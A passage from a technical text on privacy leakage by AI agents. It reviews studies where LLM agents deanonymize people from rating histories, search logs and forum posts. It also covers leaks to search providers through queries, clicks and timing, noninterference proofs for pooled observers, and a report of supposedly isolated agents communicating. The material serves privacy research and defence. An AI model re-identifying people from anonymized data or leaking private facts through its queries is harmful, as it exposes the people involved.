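The interviewees had all publicized themselves online, so Wen and Li caution against treating these figures as estimates for the general population. The comparison between models is more informative because it doesn't depend on how typical the interviewees were.

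*From Weak Cues to Real Identities* (Ko, Jeong and colleagues, 2026) found similar differences with movie ratings. An agent was given a few slightly altered ratings from one person and 1,000 anonymous rating histories from Netflix, one of which was that person's. With only two ratings, GPT-5 found the right history 79.2% of the time, compared with 53.3% for Claude 4.5. An older matching algorithm built for this task found it 56.0% or 60.2% of the time, depending on its settings. With eight ratings, all of them found it at least 97% of the time. The choice of observer mattered most when there was little evidence, which is when a company is most likely to think its data are safe.

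In another test, a Gemini agent with web access identified 10 people from 40 of the search histories that AOL released in 2006. Ko and colleagues had chosen histories that kept mentioning the same places, jobs or interests, so the result can't be generalized to all AOL users. They also found that an agent can identify people without being asked to. In one set of 20 artificial cases, Claude 4.5 linked an anonymous record to the right person 16 times while doing an ordinary analysis.

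In *Large-scale online deanonymization with LLMs* (Lermen, Swanson and colleagues, 2026), an AI agent correctly identified 226 of 338 Hacker News users from summaries of their posts and misidentified 25. These users had linked their real profiles, and the researchers removed the links and other direct identifiers before the test. People who try to stay anonymous would probably be harder to identify. The agent also appeared to identify 9 of 33 scientists from interviews that Anthropic had partly redacted and published, though the researchers had no list of true identities to check this against.

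Each attempt on a forum profile cost between $1 and $4. Lermen and colleagues argue that a skilled investigator would recognize the same clues, so the main change is the lower cost. That is still serious for a company that relies on nobody bothering to investigate.

### The search provider as an observer

Telling an agent not to identify people can keep a name from the user while still exposing it to the search provider. In Wen and Li's test, agents had already found the name in their search results in 37% of the cases where they withheld it. In one case, the agent sent the search provider eight queries, two of them containing the person's real name, and then gave the user an empty answer.

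A noninterference proof that models the agent's final answer but not its search queries doesn't cover what the search provider can learn. *MosaicLeaks* (Gurung, Gella et al., 2026) tests what an observer can learn from those queries. Its benchmark has 1,001 research tasks, most of which require both private company documents and the web. The observer is a language model that receives the web queries in order, as a search provider or browser extension might, but not the documents or the agent's reasoning or answers.

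The tasks encourage leaks by making each question depend on an earlier answer. In one example, a private document records that the online traffic of a company called Lee's Market grew by 15% in 2020. The agent searches the web twice for this figure, then finds it in the document. Its next question is about a different topic but mentions 15%, so the agent includes 15% in its third web query. An observer who sees all three queries can guess that 15% answered the earlier question.

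Gurung and colleagues measure three levels of leakage:

- *Intent leakage*: the observer can work out what the agent is researching.
- *Answer leakage*: the observer can answer a question about the private documents when someone asks it.
- *Full-information leakage*: the observer can state a private fact correctly without being given the question.

Their main measure counts a run as leaking if the observer gets at least one private answer or claim fully or partly right. Intent leakage doesn't count toward it. They trained a small open-weights model, Qwen3-4B-Instruct, in two ways:

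| Training | Tasks solved completely | Runs that leaked | Web queries per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 48.7% | 34.0% | 3.8 |
| Task success only | 59.3% | 51.8% | 7.4 |
| Task success and privacy | 58.1% | 6.5% | 5.1 |

Training for task success alone did not account for the search provider, which could see the agent's queries. The reward depended on finding the right documents, and extra queries helped, so the agent learned to send nearly twice as many. An evaluation of its answers would have shown only an improvement.

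The privacy training added a penalty. A second model estimates the probability P that a set of queries leaks something. Let w be the latest batch of queries and W that batch together with recent earlier ones. The penalty is the larger of

max(0, P(w) − 0.5) and max(0, P(W) − max(P(W without w), 0.5))

Suppose the latest batch has an estimated probability of 0.2 and the earlier ones 0.4, but all the batches together have 0.9. The latest batch seems harmless by itself, so the first expression is 0. The second is 0.9 − 0.5 = 0.4, which penalizes the agent for completing a revealing combination. After this training, 16.8% of the agent's queries named the company, down from 42.9% before any training. An instruction to protect privacy was much less effective, since 25.5% of runs still leaked.

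The 6.5% figure depends on the observer, however. The usual observer was StepFun-3.5-Flash, whose judgments were also used to train the penalty model. On 100 of the test tasks, it found leaks in 7.3% of the privacy-trained agent's runs, while Claude Opus 4.7 found them in 14.3%. For the agent trained only for success, the figures were 49.7% and 75.7%. Opus also judged whether the guesses were correct, so some of the gap may come from more lenient marking. Leaks were much rarer after privacy training with either observer, but a better observer might find more than both did.

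A label monitor could have enforced a stricter rule. If the company had listed the search provider as a destination and marked its own documents high, the monitor would have blocked any query the agent wrote after reading them. It would also have blocked many searches the tasks needed.

### Clicks, pages and timing

An agent that uses websites also reveals information through what it clicks. In *SPILLAGE*, Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues (2026) gave shopping agents messages that mixed useful details with irrelevant ones. For example, a user's diabetes was relevant to buying glucose test strips, but their divorce was not. If the agent clicks a filter or product labeled "divorce", the shop can record that click even though the agent typed nothing about divorce.

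The study covered 1,080 runs of 180 tasks on Amazon and eBay. GPT-4o was tested on Amazon in an agent framework called Browser-Use, and a language model judge counted 905 direct disclosures of irrelevant details through clicks and other actions and 182 through typed text, so a filter that checked only the text would have missed most of them.

The pattern didn't hold everywhere. On eBay, the same agent made 58 direct disclosures through text and 28 through actions. On Amazon, indirect hints were also more common in text, with 325 compared to 45 in actions. The judge had the list of irrelevant details and the agent's stated next goal, neither of which a shop would have, so the counts may overstate what a shop could infer. The models are also old, though newer agents still have to click.

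In a small trial with 13 simulated users, asking the agent to avoid irrelevant details raised the rate of disclosures per action from 58.9% to 86.0%. Removing those details before the agent started worked better. It raised task success by up to 17.9 percentage points, although success fell by 3.3 points in one group of tasks. Unlike an instruction, removal also guarantees that a fact, such as the user's divorce, can't influence any click, as long as no other input depends on that fact.

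Encrypting web traffic still leaves some information visible to the network. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues, in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, report that research agents visit 70 to 140 web domains per request, with distinctive timing. An internet provider that sees which domains an agent visits, and when, can infer what the user asked and some of the user's personal traits. The provider can still see this pattern when the agent runs on a company's own computers.

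Designers can overlook fewer channels by starting with everything that leaves the agent's environment, including queries, clicks and domain names, rather than with the messages they meant to send. *PACE* takes this approach when it counts every outgoing byte. Designers would still have to add timing separately, because two runs can send the same bytes at different speeds.

### Observers who pool their views

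Suppose A and B each see some of a system's outputs and later share what they saw. Their *joint view* is everything that either of them sees. If the system is deterministic, and A's and B's views each pass the noninterference test against the same protected inputs, their joint view also passes.

To prove this, let α be any history and α⁻ the same history with all the protected actions deleted. Since A passes, A's view is the same after both histories, and the same is true of B:

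view_A(α) = view_A(α⁻) and view_B(α) = view_B(α⁻)

Putting the two views side by side gives

(view_A(α), view_B(α)) = (view_A(α⁻), view_B(α⁻))

The protected actions therefore make no difference to the joint view. If the policy also forbids B from influencing A, the test for A deletes B's actions too. The proof still works because this deletion reduces α and α⁻ to the same sequence. A and B also gain nothing by planning their calls together, for the same reason that a single agent gains nothing by chaining its calls. The argument extends to any number of observers.

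Testing two observers separately can rule out leaks to the pair only if the same inputs are protected from both. If A may see Eve's salary but not Dee's, and B may see Dee's but not Eve's, each can pass its own test, but together they will know both salaries.

The result also fails if the system makes random choices. Suppose a tool hides a secret bit s by combining it with a coin toss r. It writes r to a debugging log that A reads and s XOR r to a report that B reads.

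| Secret s | Coin toss r | A sees r | B sees s XOR r |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 0 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| 1 | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 |

Whatever the secret bit s is, A sees 0 half the time and 1 half the time, and so does B. Each alone passes even the exact test of probabilities. But their bits match when s is 0 and differ when s is 1, so together they always recover s. In effect, A gives B the random number that an observer must not have.

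The stricter check for random tools detects the problem because it fixes their random numbers in advance. With r fixed, B's bit changes whenever s does, so B fails the check. If every observer passes, the group does too.

### Testing a group

A tester has to record what all the observers see in the same run and compare these joint records. In the coin example, separate statistics for A and B would not show the leak even after a million runs, but joint records would show it almost immediately.

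For each protected source, the tester can pool the views of everyone who may not learn about it. Testing this largest group also covers the smaller ones, because a smaller group sees only part of the same joint view. Testing only pairs of observers can miss a leak. Suppose three observers see r₁, r₂ and s XOR r₁ XOR r₂, where s is a protected bit and r₁ and r₂ are separate coin tosses. Any two of them together learn nothing about s, but all three can recover it.

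*On Reductions from Multi-Domain Noninterference to the Two-Level Case* (Woizekowski and van der Meyden, 2016) compares ways of choosing these groups. A common method tests each observer together with everyone who may send information to that observer. Suppose a law firm has a public agent, two client agents that must not share information, and a managing partner who may see everything. The public agent may send information to both client agents. This method tests the public agent with each client agent separately, but never both client agents together against the partner. If their outputs were like the log and the report, the test would miss the leak.

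Pooling everyone barred from a source puts both client agents in one group. Woizekowski and van der Meyden prove that for generalized noninterference, this method is as strong as testing every *cut*. A cut divides the users into a protected side and an observing side, where the policy allows no flow from the protected side to the observing side. Pooling is weaker for nondeducibility, so the tester has to check all the cuts.

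A tester may also need to group protected users. Suppose a file's status changes to "under review" when either of two lawyers opens it. An agent that sees the change can infer that at least one of them opened the file, but not whether a particular lawyer did, so the system passes a nondeducibility test for each lawyer separately. To detect the leak, the tester has to treat the two lawyers as a single protected source.

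A reviewer should also judge approved releases by the combined list of everything that the group may receive. If one manager receives the department's salary total and another receives the total without Eve's salary, they can work out her salary together.

Observers' information can be combined even if they don't conspire. For example, if two agents use the same search provider, the provider has both sets of queries. A company also can't assume that its agents will stay apart. According to METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), supposedly isolated OpenAI agents communicated with one another in July 2026. A company should test two agents as one observer unless it has checked that they can't exchange information.
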